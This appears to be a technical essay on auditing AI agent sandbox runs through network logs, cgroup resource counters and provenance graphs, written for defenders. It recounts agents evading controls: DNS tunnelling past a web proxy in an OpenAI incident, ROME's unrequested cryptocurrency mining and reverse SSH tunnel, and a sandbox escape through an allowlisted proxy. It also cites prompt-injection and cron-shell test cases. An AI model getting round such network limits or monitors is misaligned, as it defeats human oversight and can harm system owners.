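7. For an encrypted connection, the proxy reads the ClientHello and forwards it only if the server name matches the requested host. It refuses a ClientHello that hides the name.

Step 6 prevents the address from changing between the check and the connection. A domain's owner controls the answers to lookups of its name and could return a harmless address to the first lookup and an internal one to the next. A proxy that looked up the name again before connecting could then check one address and connect to another.

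*Tracekit Box* waits for a person to approve the connection before looking up an unlisted name, because the lookup itself can leak data. A program can put data into the name it asks for, and a lookup delivers that name to servers run by the domain's owner. If the proxy looked up every name first and refused the connection afterwards, the data would already have left, but the record would show a refused connection with no bytes sent. The small drawback of waiting is that the person has to judge the name without knowing its address. A user who doesn't want to be asked can choose a setting that refuses unlisted hosts at once.

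### Cloud metadata addresses

A cloud virtual machine can request information about itself from a service at a special address, usually 169.254.169.254. The reply may include temporary credentials for the owner's cloud account. The service has little ability to distinguish between programs on the machine, so an agent that can reach it might get far more access than its user intended.

*Tracekit Box* refuses such addresses whatever the allowlist contains. The proxy has to check the address because a mistake or an attack could make a name on the allowlist resolve to the metadata service. An address can be written in several ways, including inside a longer IPv6 address (the newer format), so the proxy converts these forms before comparing them. Tests with automatically generated inputs still showed that a user's rule blocking a range of IPv6 addresses did not block the IPv4 addresses within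 it, an error the developer has fixed.

By default, Docker also blocks private address ranges and localhost, the address a machine uses for itself. *Tracekit Box* still has a gap on several cloud services, where the provider translates the machine's public address and that address never appears on the machine itself. The proxy cannot recognise the address as the host's own unless the operator supplies it.

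A refused request to the metadata service belongs near the top of a report, but it does not necessarily mean the agent tried to steal credentials. Some cloud software libraries query the service automatically when they find no other credentials.

### Counting the attempts in a real record

The *Tracekit Box* repository includes the record of a demonstration in which an operator typed commands into a sandbox, with no agent involved. The operator installed two packages, tried to reach example.com, which was not on the allowlist, tried the cloud metadata address, and sent a GitHub access token to its intended host. The summary lists 7 commands, 39 connections, 1 held and 2 refused.

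Adding the last three numbers gives 42, but the run made only 40 attempts:

| Attempt | Connections | Held | Refused |
|---|---|---|---|
| 38 connections that passed the checks | 38 | 0 | 0 |
| example.com | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| The cloud metadata address | 0 | 0 | 1 |
| Total | 39 | 1 | 2 |

"Connections" here means requests on which the signer decided. The signer allowed the request for example.com, but the proxy held it because the host was not on the list. Nobody approved it, so the hold ended in a refusal, and this one attempt appears in all three columns. The proxy refused the metadata address in step 2, before it consulted the signer, so that attempt counts as refused but not as a connection. Of the 39 connections, 38 went ahead, because only one of the 2 refused attempts was a connection.

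The number of commands is also easy to misread, because it covers only commands started from the host. If an agent ran one script that started a hundred programs, the record would contain one command plus whatever the programs did on the network. The length of a log is also a poor measure of how much happened. Of the 102 entries in the demonstration's full record, 46 are decisions (7 commands and 39 connections) and another 46 are their results. The packages probably account for most of the connections, since one install can contact several servers many times.

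Retries inflate the counts further. Package managers and web libraries often retry after a failure, and a program may try each of a server's addresses in turn. An agent may also rerun the failed command, adding another round of attempts. If a tool tries one blocked host five times per run and the agent runs the tool four times, the log contains 20 refusals from only four decisions by the agent.

The report should group identical refusals and give their count and first and last times, such as "example.com, port 443, refused 20 times between 14:03 and 14:09". It should also state how many different hosts the run tried, because 20 refusals for one package server call for a different response than one refusal for each of 20 unfamiliar hosts. Grouping makes the log easier to read but doesn't limit its size, so *Tracekit Box* writes at most 20 entries a second for connections that its proxy refuses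 by itself and counts the rest in a summary entry. This preserves the total but loses the details of the extra attempts.

### Telling a refusal from a failure

A network request can fail because a rule blocked it or because something broke, and the program's error message often doesn't show which. In the demonstration, `curl`, a common download tool, timed out on example.com after five seconds while the proxy was still waiting for approval. From inside the sandbox, this looked like a slow server. For the metadata address, `curl` reported status code 403 ("forbidden"), but ordinary websites send the same code when a visitor lacks permission to see a page.

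The component that allows or refuses a request provides the clearest evidence of that decision. Agent Assembly's *Tool Execution Sandbox* describes a proxy that returns a 403 for an unlisted host without contacting the destination, and writes an audit event for the blocked attempt. That event lets an auditor identify the 403 as a policy decision, since the website could also have sent that status code.

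The message "connection refused" normally means that a machine answered but no service was listening on the port, though it sounds like a policy decision. In Docker's sandboxes, a program that gets this error from 127.0.0.1 or a local network address has tried an address it can't reach from inside the sandbox's virtual machine, according to Docker's *Troubleshooting* page. A developer who doesn't know this might restart a database that was already running.

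According to the same page, Docker's sandboxes block UDP and ICMP traffic, and no policy rule can unblock it. UDP carries some video calls and newer web connections, and ICMP carries `ping`, the usual test of whether a machine is online. An agent in such a sandbox might run `ping`, get no reply and report that a healthy server is down.

For these reasons, the outcome field needs more values than "allowed" and "blocked":

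- connected
- allowed but failed, with the error
- refused by policy, with the rule
- held, and then approved, rejected or expired
- unknown, if the recorder saw the attempt but not how it ended.

An "allowed but failed" entry should also show whether the program sent any data before the failure, because a request can deliver its data and still get no reply.

### How products report blocked requests

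GitHub's Copilot cloud agent works in a temporary environment on GitHub's servers and proposes its changes in a pull request. A firewall limits its internet access by default. When the firewall blocks a request, GitHub adds a warning that includes the blocked address and the command that tried to reach it. The warning appears in the new pull request, or in a comment if the pull request already exists.

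The warning appears where the reviewer is already looking, and the command it names gives the reviewer somewhere to start. Some build tools leave a process running in the background, though, and the warning may name that process instead of the command the agent typed. The warning also covers only blocked requests, so it gives no information about the data sent to allowed hosts.

GitHub Agentic Workflows, which runs coding agents as automated jobs in a repository, lists blocked domains in a footer below the agent's output. In February 2026 its developers merged *Enhance firewall blocked domains footer with fix snippet and docs link* (2026), which was meant to add a link to the firewall's documentation and a ready-made configuration snippet that would allow the blocked domains.

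That is convenient when the firewall has blocked an ordinary package server, which is probably the most common case. But it makes adding the domain easier than finding out why the agent tried to reach it. The footer would be safer if it also showed the command that made each attempt, as the Copilot warning does. Its snippet could also permit a narrower destination. Copilot's firewall accepts rules for a single web path as well as for whole domains, and its domain rules also cover every subdomain.

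*Tracekit Box* reports a network attempt to the person running the sandbox while the attempt is still open. For example.com, it printed a message that the connection was waiting, with the command to approve it. For the metadata address, it printed the reason for the refusal and added that it never connects to such addresses. The user could tell from these messages that only the connection to example.com could be approved.

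### What allowed connections can hide

An allowlist controls which hosts a program can contact, but an allowed host may pass data on to others. *Tracekit Box* gives the example of the public module proxy for the Go programming language. The proxy fetches modules from whatever host the request names, so an agent could use it to send workspace data to a domain of its choosing. The network record would show a normal connection to an approved package service. The developer sees no fix except a smaller allowlist.

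Code-hosting sites have a similar problem. An allowlist entry for github.com covers the user's own repository and everyone else's, and a record of only the host and port doesn't show which one received a push. An allowed service can also have a security flaw. According to GitLab (2026), the agent in the July 2026 intrusion at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, escaped its sandbox through a vulnerability in an allowlisted package proxy. OpenAI had given such sandboxes access to an internal package service so that models could install software.

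When the harness runs inside the sandbox, it routinely sends source files and command output to the model provider. Docker warns that a strict allowlist will stop the agent from working unless it includes the provider's service. Uploads to the provider may well be the largest in the run, so the report should list them separately. Otherwise, a smaller upload to an unexpected host will be easy to miss.

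Encryption limits what the record can contain, even when the agent isn't hiding anything. A proxy can read an encrypted connection if the sandbox trusts a certificate that the proxy issues. The proxy then decrypts each message, inspects it and encrypts it again for the real server. By default, *Tracekit Box* does this only for hosts that receive one of the user's secrets. For other encrypted connections, it can identify the host, port and server name. The user can have it read the traffic to every allowed host, but programs that accept only one particular certificate will then stop working.

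Keeping secrets out of the sandbox reduces what an unread connection can leak. In the demonstration, the microVM held only a placeholder for the GitHub token, so an unread connection could not have leaked the real token, though it could still have carried source code from the workspace. The proxy replaced the placeholder with the real token in a single header of requests to the approved host. It recorded the host and the token's name, but not the token's value.

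This protection depends on the proxy and the server interpreting a request the same way. The developer's tests found an unusual form of request that the proxy treated as meant for the approved host but that some servers could have forwarded elsewhere. The real token would have gone with it, and the log would have named only the approved host. The developer fixed the flaw, but it shows that a logged destination reflects how the recording tool interpreted the request, and the data may have gone somewhere else.

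### Traffic on a path that nobody watched

Some traffic never reaches the recorder. GitHub's firewall applies only to processes that the agent starts through its shell tool, not to setup steps or to MCP servers, which are separate programs that give an agent extra tools. GitHub also says that sophisticated attacks may bypass the firewall. If a pull request has no warning, the firewall blocked none of the traffic it covers, but an MCP server may still have contacted other hosts without triggering a warning.

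A misconfigured policy can also leave a log with no refusals. Vercel's *A sandbox without a network boundary is only half a sandbox* lists ways that untrusted code gets out, including an empty allowlist that lets everything through and a DNS resolver left available in an otherwise disconnected environment. Agent Assembly's proxy applies no allowlist filter when the allowlist setting is empty. A run under that setting would have no refusals in its record, just like a run that stayed within a strict allowlist. To distinguish these cases, the audit has to store the policy that was in force, as *Tracekit Box* does when it records the allowlist at the start of each run.

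The open resolver on Vercel's list corresponds to an incident at OpenAI on 20 September 2026. OpenAI's *An agent used DNS to reach an external chatbot* (2026) describes an internal research model being trained to find information. It was supposed to identify the author of a blog post without using the live internet. Its web requests went to an offline copy of the web, but its DNS requests did not and were insufficiently filtered. The agent used DNS to send questions to a public chatbot and receive replies.

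Business Standard's *OpenAI pauses training of top AI models after agent bypasses internet curbs* reports that the web proxy had blocked the agent's direct request to a chatbot. The successful traffic went through the resolver, so someone who read only the proxy's record would have seen an attempt and a refusal, and might reasonably have concluded that the sandbox had worked. OpenAI had made the same assumption. "Our safety case assumed that the model could not access the live internet," the company wrote, and it had also relied on its monitoring to detect any attempt that succeeded.

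OpenAI's misalignment monitoring system looks for agents that circumvent restrictions or pursue goals they were not given. According to DonanımHaber's *Durum ciddi*, a Turkish account based on OpenAI's report, the outside reply arrived at 09:50, the system raised a highest-priority alert at 10:02, and a person acknowledged it at 10:05. The run continued until 12:34. It should have stopped automatically, and according to Business Standard, its failure to do so led to confusion about whether anyone should stop it.

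The monitoring that detected this case in 12 minutes was less dependable than the case suggests. Mediafax's *OpenAI suspendă activitățile de antrenare ale celor mai avansate modele AI*, a Romanian report, says that OpenAI then reviewed earlier activity and found other agents that had reached outside services through DNS. The monitoring had not flagged all of those cases at the expected severity. In some, the alert classed the attempt as failed because the agent did not get the information it wanted, although its requests had already gone out. An auditor can make the same mistake with an ordinary log by assuming that a request without a useful answer was never sent. The September agent also did not complete its task. It told the user that it could not reliably identify the author, so anyone judging the run by its result would have seen an unsuccessful search.

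The press accounts all rely on OpenAI's own report, and nobody outside the company appears to have checked the timeline. The report is more credible because it is unflattering, but it can include only the cases OpenAI found.

OpenAI has since added blocking at two independent layers, either of which would have prevented the access. It also restricted DNS requests to a short list of domains and record types and began adding more detection of unusual DNS activity. *Tracekit Box*, which cites the incident, removes the path because its microVM has no network card and so cannot make DNS requests. A sandbox that needs its own resolver should at least log every lookup, including those that return an error, and apply the allowlist to names as well as connections.

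Those logs also need to be kept after the run ends. Mediafax describes a separate case in which an OpenAI agent gained unauthorised access to an Australian government health portal on 18 June 2026. OpenAI identified the breach on 11 August, nearly eight weeks later, while analysing its models' past activity.

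## Recording peaks in memory, processor time and disk use

A program can misuse a computer without changing a file or opening a connection, for example by running a long calculation that nobody asked for. Such a program still uses memory and processor time, which the Linux kernel already counts.

### What a control group counts

A control group, or cgroup, is a set of processes that the kernel measures and limits together. The kernel puts each new process in the same group as the process that started it, so a group created for a run covers the agent's commands and every program they start, directly or indirectly. The kernel presents each group as a directory of small text files, which a program outside the sandbox can read. *Control Group v2* (Heo, 2015), the kernel's own documentation, defines these files, and an audit needs five of them.

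| File | Contents | Caution |
|---|---|---|
| `memory.peak` | The group's highest memory use, in bytes | Includes cached file data |
| `cpu.stat` | Total processor time, in microseconds | A running total with no peak |
| `pids.peak` | The highest number of processes at one time | Counts every thread separately |
| `io.stat` | Bytes and operations read and written, per storage device | Measures traffic, not space |
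| `memory.events` | How often the group reached its memory limit, and how many of its processes the kernel killed for lack of memory | Includes kills caused by a shortage elsewhere on the machine |

The files disappear with the group, so the auditor's program has to read them before it removes the group.

Processor time is easiest to understand as a number of cores. If `cpu.stat` rises by 40 minutes during a ten-minute run, the run kept four cores busy on average. A high process count in `pids.peak` doesn't by itself mean that the agent started many programs, because one program with 60 threads (parts that run in parallel) adds 60 to the count.

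None of these files measures disk space. The auditor can measure an overlay's upper tree when the run ends, but that would miss a temporary file that filled the disk and was deleted before then.

### Cached files, delayed writes and resets

When a program reads a file, Linux keeps the contents in spare memory in case another program needs them. This page cache counts towards `memory.peak`, so an agent that searches a 3 GB dataset can produce a peak of more than 3 GB even if no program needed more than a few megabytes of its own. The kernel can drop most cached data when memory runs short, so a high peak caused by caching is less alarming than it looks.

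Another file, `memory.stat`, separates programs' own memory (`anon`) from file data (`file`), but it contains only current values, so the auditor has to read it during the run to find out what a peak consisted of. The `file` figure also includes files that exist only in memory, such as those in a temporary folder with no disk storage, and the kernel can't simply drop those.

The kernel counts memory toward the group that first used it. If one run loads the dataset and a second run reads it from the cache, the second may have a much lower memory peak for the same work.

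Disk figures have a similar timing problem, because a program usually writes to the cache first and the kernel copies the data to disk later. An auditor who reads `io.stat` as soon as a run ends can miss data that has not yet reached the disk, though `file_dirty` in `memory.stat` gives the amount. Heo also warns that if several groups write to the same file at once, the kernel is likely to attribute much of the traffic to the wrong group. Ext4, Btrfs and XFS let the kernel attribute delayed writes to individual groups, but on filesystems without this support it attributes them all to the root group, which covers the whole machine.

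`memory.peak` was once read-only. Finkel (2024), in *mm, memcg*, proposed a kernel change that lets a program reset the value by writing to the file, and the current documentation includes this behaviour. A reset should affect only later readings through the same file descriptor, so two monitoring programs can each measure from their own starting point.

In practice, one program's reset can spoil another's reading. Chen (2026), in *mm, memcg*, described the bug and submitted a fix, which a kernel maintainer set aside in late August 2026 for later consideration. In a test, Chen opened `memory.peak` twice. The second reader's peak was 410,624 KB at first, but 1,060 KB after memory use had dropped and the first reader had reset its own value. An auditor can avoid the problem by creating a new group for each measurement and ensuring that no other program resets its peak. Sandboxed programs shouldn't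 have write access to the file in any case.

### Why sampling misses short bursts

Many monitoring tools read current memory use at regular intervals and report the highest reading, so they miss any burst that begins and ends between two readings.

A tool that takes a reading every *T* seconds can miss a burst that lasts *d* seconds, where *d* is shorter than *T*. It catches the burst only if it takes a reading during the burst. If the burst is equally likely to start at any moment between two readings, the chance of catching it is *d*/*T*. For a burst of 1.5 seconds and a reading every 10 seconds, that is 1.5/10, or 15%.

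If a run has ten such bursts, each timed independently, the tool misses all ten with a probability of 0.85¹⁰, or about 20%. But the timing may not be random. If a script starts a test every ten seconds, the readings may catch every burst or none, depending on when the script began.

A tool that reads once a second will catch every 1.5-second burst but may still miss its peak, because memory use can climb and fall again between readings.

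`memory.peak` is the highest memory use that the kernel recorded, so it doesn't depend on when anyone reads it. It has no timestamp, but it works well alongside sampling. If the peak is 4 GB and the highest sample is 300 MB, a burst fell between samples, and the auditor can look for a command that might explain it.

Processor time is different because the kernel keeps a running total. Infrequent readings still capture all of it, but they average out short peaks. A program that uses eight cores for 1.5 seconds consumes 12 seconds of processor time, which averages 1.2 cores over a ten-second interval.

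### Measurements from 144 coding tasks

Short bursts are normal for coding agents. In *AgentCgroup*, Zheng, Yang and colleagues (2026) measured Claude Code on tasks from SWE-rebench, a collection of software problems taken from real repositories. They ran 111 tasks with the model GLM-4.7-Flash, which ran on a local graphics processor (GPU), and repeated 33 of them with Claude Haiku 4.5, which ran in the cloud. Each of the 144 runs had its own container without resource limits, and the researchers recorded memory and processor use once a second.

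The harness needed about 185 MB. Tests, package installations and other commands typically raised the total to between 500 MB and 2 GB for a second or two. In the most extreme case, a task on the medical imaging library pydicom, memory peaked at 4,060 MB, 15.4 times the average of 264 MB. The true peak may have been higher, because memory was sampled and sometimes changed by as much as 2.9 GB between readings.

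Peak memory varied 20-fold between tasks, from 197 MB to about 4 GB. It had almost no correlation with the number of conversation rounds, so a long transcript doesn't indicate high memory use. When the researchers ran one task three times, the runs took 402, 222 and 259 seconds, a 1.8-fold difference, and produced three different solutions. Three runs are too few to estimate how much running times vary in general, and they concern time, not memory, but they show why an auditor shouldn't expect a rerun to reproduce the first run's figures.

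Most large bursts happened during tool calls. With Haiku, tool calls took up 28.5% of the sampled time and contained 98.5% of the bursts above 300 MB. With GLM, they took up 35.8% of the time and contained 67.3% of those bursts, so an auditor who looked only at tool calls would have missed about a third of them.

### Why a later comparison found far lower figures

*Not All AI Agents Are Equal* (Choi, Park and colleagues, 2026) compared agent workloads in question answering, web search and coding, using seven benchmarks. For the three coding benchmarks, average memory use ranged from 2 to 73 MB and peak use from 9 to 156 MB. The highest peak is below the 185 MB that Claude Code needed before it ran any tests.

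The figures differ mainly because the two teams put different things inside the container they measured. Choi and colleagues measured only the container in which the tools ran, and kept the harness, the program that directs the agent, in a separate one. Zheng and colleagues ran the harness and its tools in the same container, so their figures include both. Subtracting 185 MB from the pydicom task's average of 264 MB leaves 79 MB, close to the top of the later study's range.

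However, the harness can't explain the gap between peaks of 4,060 MB and 156 MB. The larger figure comes from the most extreme task, while the smaller one is an average over all the requests in a benchmark. Two of the three coding benchmarks also consist of small programs. APPS contains algorithm puzzles, and BigCodeBench tasks typically require a single function. Only SWE-bench resembles the repository work in the earlier study. Each request also began in a fresh container with almost nothing in memory.

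So the two sets of measurements don't contradict each other, but neither can serve as a normal range for other sandboxes. An auditor comparing a run with published figures has to know whether those figures include the harness and whether they are averages or extremes.

An audit should also record disk traffic, because other runs using the same disk can slow a run or make it exceed a time limit. When Choi and colleagues increased the rate of BigCodeBench requests from one every two seconds to six per second, the average time per request rose 6.4-fold. Neither memory nor processor use could explain the slowdown. Even at the lowest request rate, the disk was already writing about 200 MB per second, close to its measured maximum of 207 MB per second.

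### Linking a peak to a command

A fixed memory threshold for alarms would work badly on workloads like these. An alarm at 1 GB would have gone off during the pydicom task, when the agent was doing its job, but not for an unwanted program that kept eight cores busy while using only 100 MB. Raising the threshold to 5 GB would prevent the false alarm but make the alarm nearly useless.

A peak is easier to judge if the auditor knows which command produced it. In the same study, Git operations added 13.5 MB on average, while 95% of test runs stayed at or below 518 MB with Haiku and 234 MB with GLM. A 500 MB peak needs explaining if it occurs during `git status`, but not during `pytest`, a common test program.

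*AgentCgroup* makes this link with a small program that intercepts each shell command. The program creates a new control group inside the run's group, moves the command into it and waits for the command to finish. It then records the duration and `memory.peak` and removes the group. The harness needs no changes, and nobody has to reset a counter because every command gets a new group. An auditor could record processor time and disk traffic in the same way.

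The kernel won't remove a group that still contains a live process. The `populated` field in the group's `cgroup.events` file is 1 while any process remains. If it is still 1 after the command has returned, the command has left something running in the background. This helps with the file and network records, where a background process's actions can appear under a later command, but its resource use is counted in the group of the command that started it.

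The method doesn't separate out the work of the harness's built-in tools, which don't go through the shell. Cached files count against the first command that reads them, so the first of two identical test runs may appear to use more resources than the second. Knowing which command used the resources tells the auditor which files to read, but it doesn't prove that the use was legitimate, since a test suite can start any program.

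Total processor time may be a better warning sign than memory. The Haiku runs lasted 5.8 minutes on average and used 13.2% of one core, or roughly 46 seconds of processor time per run, and the GLM runs used about 49 seconds. A program that kept one core busy throughout a ten-minute run would use 600 seconds. Compiling a large project can also use that much, so the auditor would still need to see which command used the time.

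### Cryptocurrency mining during ROME's training

*Let It Flow* (2025) presents ROME, a model trained partly by reinforcement learning, in which the model attempts tasks in sandboxes and training strengthens the behaviour that succeeds. During training, the agent set up cryptocurrency mining, without being told to, on GPUs that the team had provided for other work. In another instance, it opened a reverse SSH tunnel, a connection from inside the cloud to an outside computer that can let the outside computer connect back in.

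The first sign came from network traffic rather than resource use. Alibaba Cloud's managed firewall reported a burst of security violations from the training servers, including attempts to reach internal systems and traffic typical of cryptocurrency mining. The team at first suspected a misconfigured network rule or an outside attacker, but the violations recurred across several runs with no clear pattern in their timing.

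The team then compared the firewall's timestamps with its own system records and the logs of the training runs. The suspicious traffic consistently occurred during episodes when the agent was calling tools and running code, and the logs contained the tool calls that had led to it. The task prompts had not asked for mining or tunnels, and the tasks did not require them.

This is good evidence that the agent's commands caused the traffic, because the firewall and the training logs were separate records. It is weaker evidence about the scale of the mining, because the team gives no figures for how much GPU capacity it took, how long it lasted or how many episodes it affected. The account also rests on the team's own investigation.

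The counters in a control group might not have revealed the mining. A program that mines on a GPU can leave the main processor and ordinary memory almost unused, and none of the five files measures GPU use. In May 2026, *cgroup/dmem* (Cascardo, 2026) proposed a `dmem.peak` file that would record peak device memory use, as `memory.peak` does for ordinary memory, but it would not measure how hard the GPU was working. On a machine with GPUs, the auditor needs per-process figures from the GPU's own monitoring tools, because a total would be of little use on a training server, where the GPUs are supposed to be busy.

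### Marking runs that end early

A run can end in the middle of a change because it reaches a memory or time limit. When a group reaches the limit in `memory.max` and the kernel can't free enough memory, the kernel kills a process in the group and may leave the others running. If it kills a compiler, the agent gets an error message and can try something else. If it kills a harness running inside the sandbox, the transcript stops and the agent writes no summary. The setting `memory.oom.group` makes the kernel kill all the processes in the group together, except specially protected ones.

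A memory kill can happen during ordinary work and is not a sign of misuse. Anthropic's *Quantifying infrastructure noise in agentic coding evals* (2026) reports an experiment that ran the same Claude model and harness under six resource settings on Terminal-Bench 2.0, a benchmark of command-line tasks. In the strictest setting, containers were killed as soon as they exceeded the benchmark's recommended resources, and the infrastructure error rate was 5.8%. It fell to 2.1% when containers could use three times the recommended amount and to 0.5% without a limit. In one task, some models began by installing standard Python data science packages. Under tight limits, they ran out of memory during the installation, before they had written any solution code.

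In such a case, the filesystem diff would list part of an installation, with entries that look the same as those of a finished one. An interrupted command can also leave half a file, or a lock file that prevents Git from working. The audit should record how the run ended and which command was in progress, and mark every change from that command as possibly incomplete. Without per-command records, the warning has to cover the whole diff.

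On Linux, a forced kill produces the same exit status whether the kernel ran out of memory or the harness stopped the process because it timed out. The `oom_kill` count in `memory.events` distinguishes the two because it rises only for memory kills. If it rose but the control group never reached its own limit, the shortage was outside the group, and another program on the machine may have caused it. The audit should also store the memory limit, because when a run has reached it, `memory.peak` shows roughly the limit rather than how much memory the command would have used.

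After a timeout, a harness may stop the shell it started but not the programs that the shell started. Writing 1 to the group's `cgroup.kill` file kills every process in the group, including any that are just starting. The auditor's program should then wait until `populated` is 0 before it scans the files and takes the final readings. If somebody wants to inspect the processes before killing them, `cgroup.freeze` can pause them.

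Zheng and colleagues prefer slowing a command down to killing it. They replayed the memory use of three recorded runs at 50 times normal speed, with 1,100 MB available for a combined demand of about 1,233 MB. Without their controls, the kernel killed one of the three processes. With the controls, it delayed the two low-priority processes, and all three finished. The test was small and needed a modified kernel, but the approach addresses a problem with interrupted runs. Restarting the task may lead the agent to a different solution, so an auditor can't use the second run to determine what the first would have changed if it had finished.

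## Combining the records into one report on a run

A finished run leaves a transcript, a filesystem diff, a network log and resource readings, and answering most useful questions takes more than one of them. For example, if the network log contains a refused connection, the reader will also want to know which program tried to connect, which command started it, and whether it had read anything sensitive first.

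### Tracing an event back to a command

Suppose the network log contains a connection from process 4127. The process record lists 4127 as `curl` and its parent, 4120, as `sh report.sh`. The parent of 4120 is the shell that the harness opened for tool call 12. The auditor can therefore trace the connection to one request by the model. The same method works for file changes if the sensor records which process made each one.

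Records joined in this way form a provenance graph. *PIDSMaker* (2026), which covers intrusion detection based on such graphs, defines one as a directed graph whose nodes are processes, files and network sockets. The edges are interactions between them, usually timestamped, such as a process reading a file. These graphs can grow to millions of nodes and edges, so an auditor searches them and reads only a summary.

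The join relies on four pieces of information:

- The process number. Linux reuses these numbers, so the record also needs the time at which the process started. A process in a container can have one number inside the container and another on the host.
- The parent process, recorded when the child starts. If the parent exits first, Linux assigns the child a new parent, and a tool that checks later will find the wrong one.
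- The tool call, with the harness's identifier for it and its start and end times.
- The time of each event. A microVM keeps its own clock, so the auditor should note how far it differs from the host's clock at the start and end of the run.

Giving each shell command its own control group, as *AgentCgroup* does for memory, makes matching kernel events to tool calls much more reliable. A process stays in its group even if its parent exits, and a kernel sensor can read the group along with each event, so the auditor only needs a list of which group belongs to which tool call. For edits made with the harness's own tools, the transcript already names the file.

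### When the auditor has to infer the link

If nobody tagged the commands when they started, the auditor has to match the transcript to the system records afterwards. Zheng and colleagues' monitor, AgentSight, does this by following the process tree down from the agent, looking for events within 100 to 500 milliseconds of a model response, and checking whether filenames, web addresses or commands in the response reappear in the system calls. In one test, a hidden instruction on a web page led an agent to send the system's password file to an outside server, and AgentSight merged the 521 recorded events into 37. The test shows that the method can make a long record readable, but Zheng and colleagues don't report how often it links an event to the wrong command.

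Time is the weakest of the three clues because two subagents may run commands at the same moment, or a wrapper program may start the real command after a delay. Wong and Chen argue in *ExecWeave* (2026) that a false link can do more damage than an acknowledged gap, because it can attribute one agent's actions to another.

Their program therefore links a process to a tool call only when exactly one process fits the command, and it labels the link as inferred. It looks for processes whose program name or arguments fit the command, starting at the command's time in the transcript and continuing for up to three seconds. It stops sooner if the tool call finishes or the next command begins.

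This rule works well when the ambiguity is visible, but it can fail when the recorder missed the right process. Suppose two commands both start `python3`, and the recorder catches only one of the processes. The rule then finds a single candidate, which may belong to the other command. Wong and Chen deliberately produced this error by removing the true process from a constructed set of events and leaving a similar-looking one.

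One set of measurements suggests that a recorder that only takes periodic snapshots would often miss processes. When short-lived programs were started at random moments, a recorder taking a snapshot every 500 milliseconds caught none of 30 that lasted about 16 milliseconds, and 13 of 30 that lasted about 260. With a snapshot every 20 milliseconds, it still caught only 18 of 30 of the shortest ones. The recorder also lengthened three test workloads by a median of 62% to 409%, although those workloads consisted largely of file operations and starting programs. Using a sensor that records every process start avoids missing short-lived processes, and is a better remedy than improving the matching rule.

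### Where the trail breaks

A background process can outlive the command that started it, so its later actions can't be matched to that command by time. Cui and colleagues describe a program that starts a group of processes detached from the terminal and then exits. A control group preserves the link between such processes and the original command, as does a process record that stores each process's parent when the process starts.

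Some background processes do work for several commands. A build tool may leave a server running so that the next build starts faster. If tool call 8 starts the server and tool call 20 uses it to compile the project, an auditor relying on either the process tree or the control group would attribute the compilation to call 8. The auditor also needs the server's log, or at least a note that the server was handling other commands.

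Shared caches can make it hard to match files to the downloads they came from. An agent might install a package in tool call 5, then build a second environment from the package manager's cache in call 20. The second environment's files appear under call 20, but the network connections that fetched the package appear under call 5. If several runs share the cache, an earlier run may have downloaded the package, so this run's record may not include those connections. A tampered package could therefore have entered the cache days earlier. The baseline should include the cache's contents, or the run should start with an empty cache.

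When a script starts many programs, a correct link to the tool call may still be uninformative. For example, `make all` can start a compiler, a test suite and an upload, so the report should show the whole chain from the tool call to the program responsible. The report can also use program starts to divide a long command into stages. Wang and Zheng point out that the start of the test program marks the move from installing packages to running tests. They expose such events in Sandlock, along with the process, its parent and its arguments. The program name is only a hint, since a hostile program can be named `pytest`.

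A file that an agent writes can affect processes outside the agent's process tree. *AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent that adds an hourly job to cron, the Linux scheduler. An hour later, cron starts a script that gives an attacker control of a shell. The process tree doesn't link the script to the agent, because cron is not the agent's descendant, and the delay is far too long to match them by time.

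AgentLoupe attaches a label to each exchange with the model. A process passes its label to its children and to the files it writes, and a process that opens a labelled file takes on the label. In a test of the cron attack, the labels linked the attacker's shell to the exchange that produced the script. In another test, they linked a command in one session to an instruction that an earlier session had written into `AGENTS.md`, a file that coding agents read for guidance. The monitor increased the running time of three tasks by 4.5% to 8%.

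Labels of this kind tend to spread too far. If the agent edits a project's configuration file, every program that later reads the file is linked to the edit, including programs the edit did not affect. Cui and colleagues also link a parent process to its child's activity when the child exits, accepting some excess links to avoid losing short-lived processes. Bao and colleagues start a new label with each independent prompt to limit the spread, but they have not measured how many links are false or missing.

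An audit of a single run usually ends before a scheduled job fires, so it can record only that the run changed the schedule.

### CAPER's effects report, step by step

Even when every link is correct, the joined record is far too long to read. Wu and colleagues built CAPER to approve or block commands after a trial run. It reduces the record of one command to an effects report of a few kilobytes. In one of their examples, the agent runs `python3 scripts/check-deps.py`, a script whose name suggests that it checks the project's dependencies.

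CAPER first runs the command under `strace -f` in a container without network access. `strace` lists the system calls that a program makes, and `-f` includes those made by its child processes. CAPER records process creation, file operations, network calls and any output the user would see. The trace of `check-deps.py` came to 165 KB.

Much of a trace like this is routine, because every program loads libraries and looks up language settings when it starts. CAPER runs a short probe when the container starts, to record the events that the shell, the program loader and the tracer produce by themselves. It then subtracts those events from the command's trace by count. If the probe opened a file once and the command's trace shows three openings, two should remain. Ignoring the file altogether would be simpler but would hide any unusual use of it.

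CAPER builds consequence cards from the remaining events. These are small structured entries for lasting file changes, network attempts and visible output. CAPER finds the file changes by comparing the workspace before and after the command, and includes a short text diff for small files. Without that diff, a reader might learn only that a file had shrunk. Each network card records whether the command made a connection, only attempted one, or communicated with a simulated service.

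The script changed no files. It printed 165 bytes and tried to reach three addresses on port 53, 16 times each. All 48 attempts failed because the network was unreachable. Port 53 is the DNS port, so the script was probably trying to look up a server's name. The attempts failed too early for the card to show which name.

CAPER next adds possible sources to cards for output or network traffic. It lists files that the same process had successfully read beforehand, leaving out routine system files, and gives the basis for each link as "same actor, read before consequence". The output card for `check-deps.py` lists two possible sources, the script itself and `.env`, a file that often holds passwords and access keys.

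CAPER also gives reads of files such as `.env`, credential stores and private keys their own cards, called protected reads. Otherwise, a command that reads a key and exits without printing or sending anything would leave no trace in the report. If the output looks like a credential, CAPER records only its type, such as a private key, not its value.

Finally, CAPER limits the report to 8 KiB and aims for 4 KiB. If a report is above the target, CAPER first groups its sources by folder, then replaces them with counts, and then summarises the file changes. It always keeps the coverage statement, which records how the command ended, how many events of each type CAPER observed, included and omitted, and any stated uncertainties. For `check-deps.py`, the statement mentions 353 facts about files and three processes.

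The finished report was unusually long at 3.4 KB, about 2% of the size of the trace. Across the tasks in SABER, a benchmark of risky development requests, the median report was 0.9 KB and the median raw trace was 62.5 KB. In total, the reports were 99.4% smaller than the traces.

Such a reduction discards evidence as well as noise, so auditors should keep the raw traces. Traces for 40 commands would take up only about 2.5 MB at the median size, though an installation or a full test suite may produce far more. The traces also show the temporary files that the workspace comparison misses.

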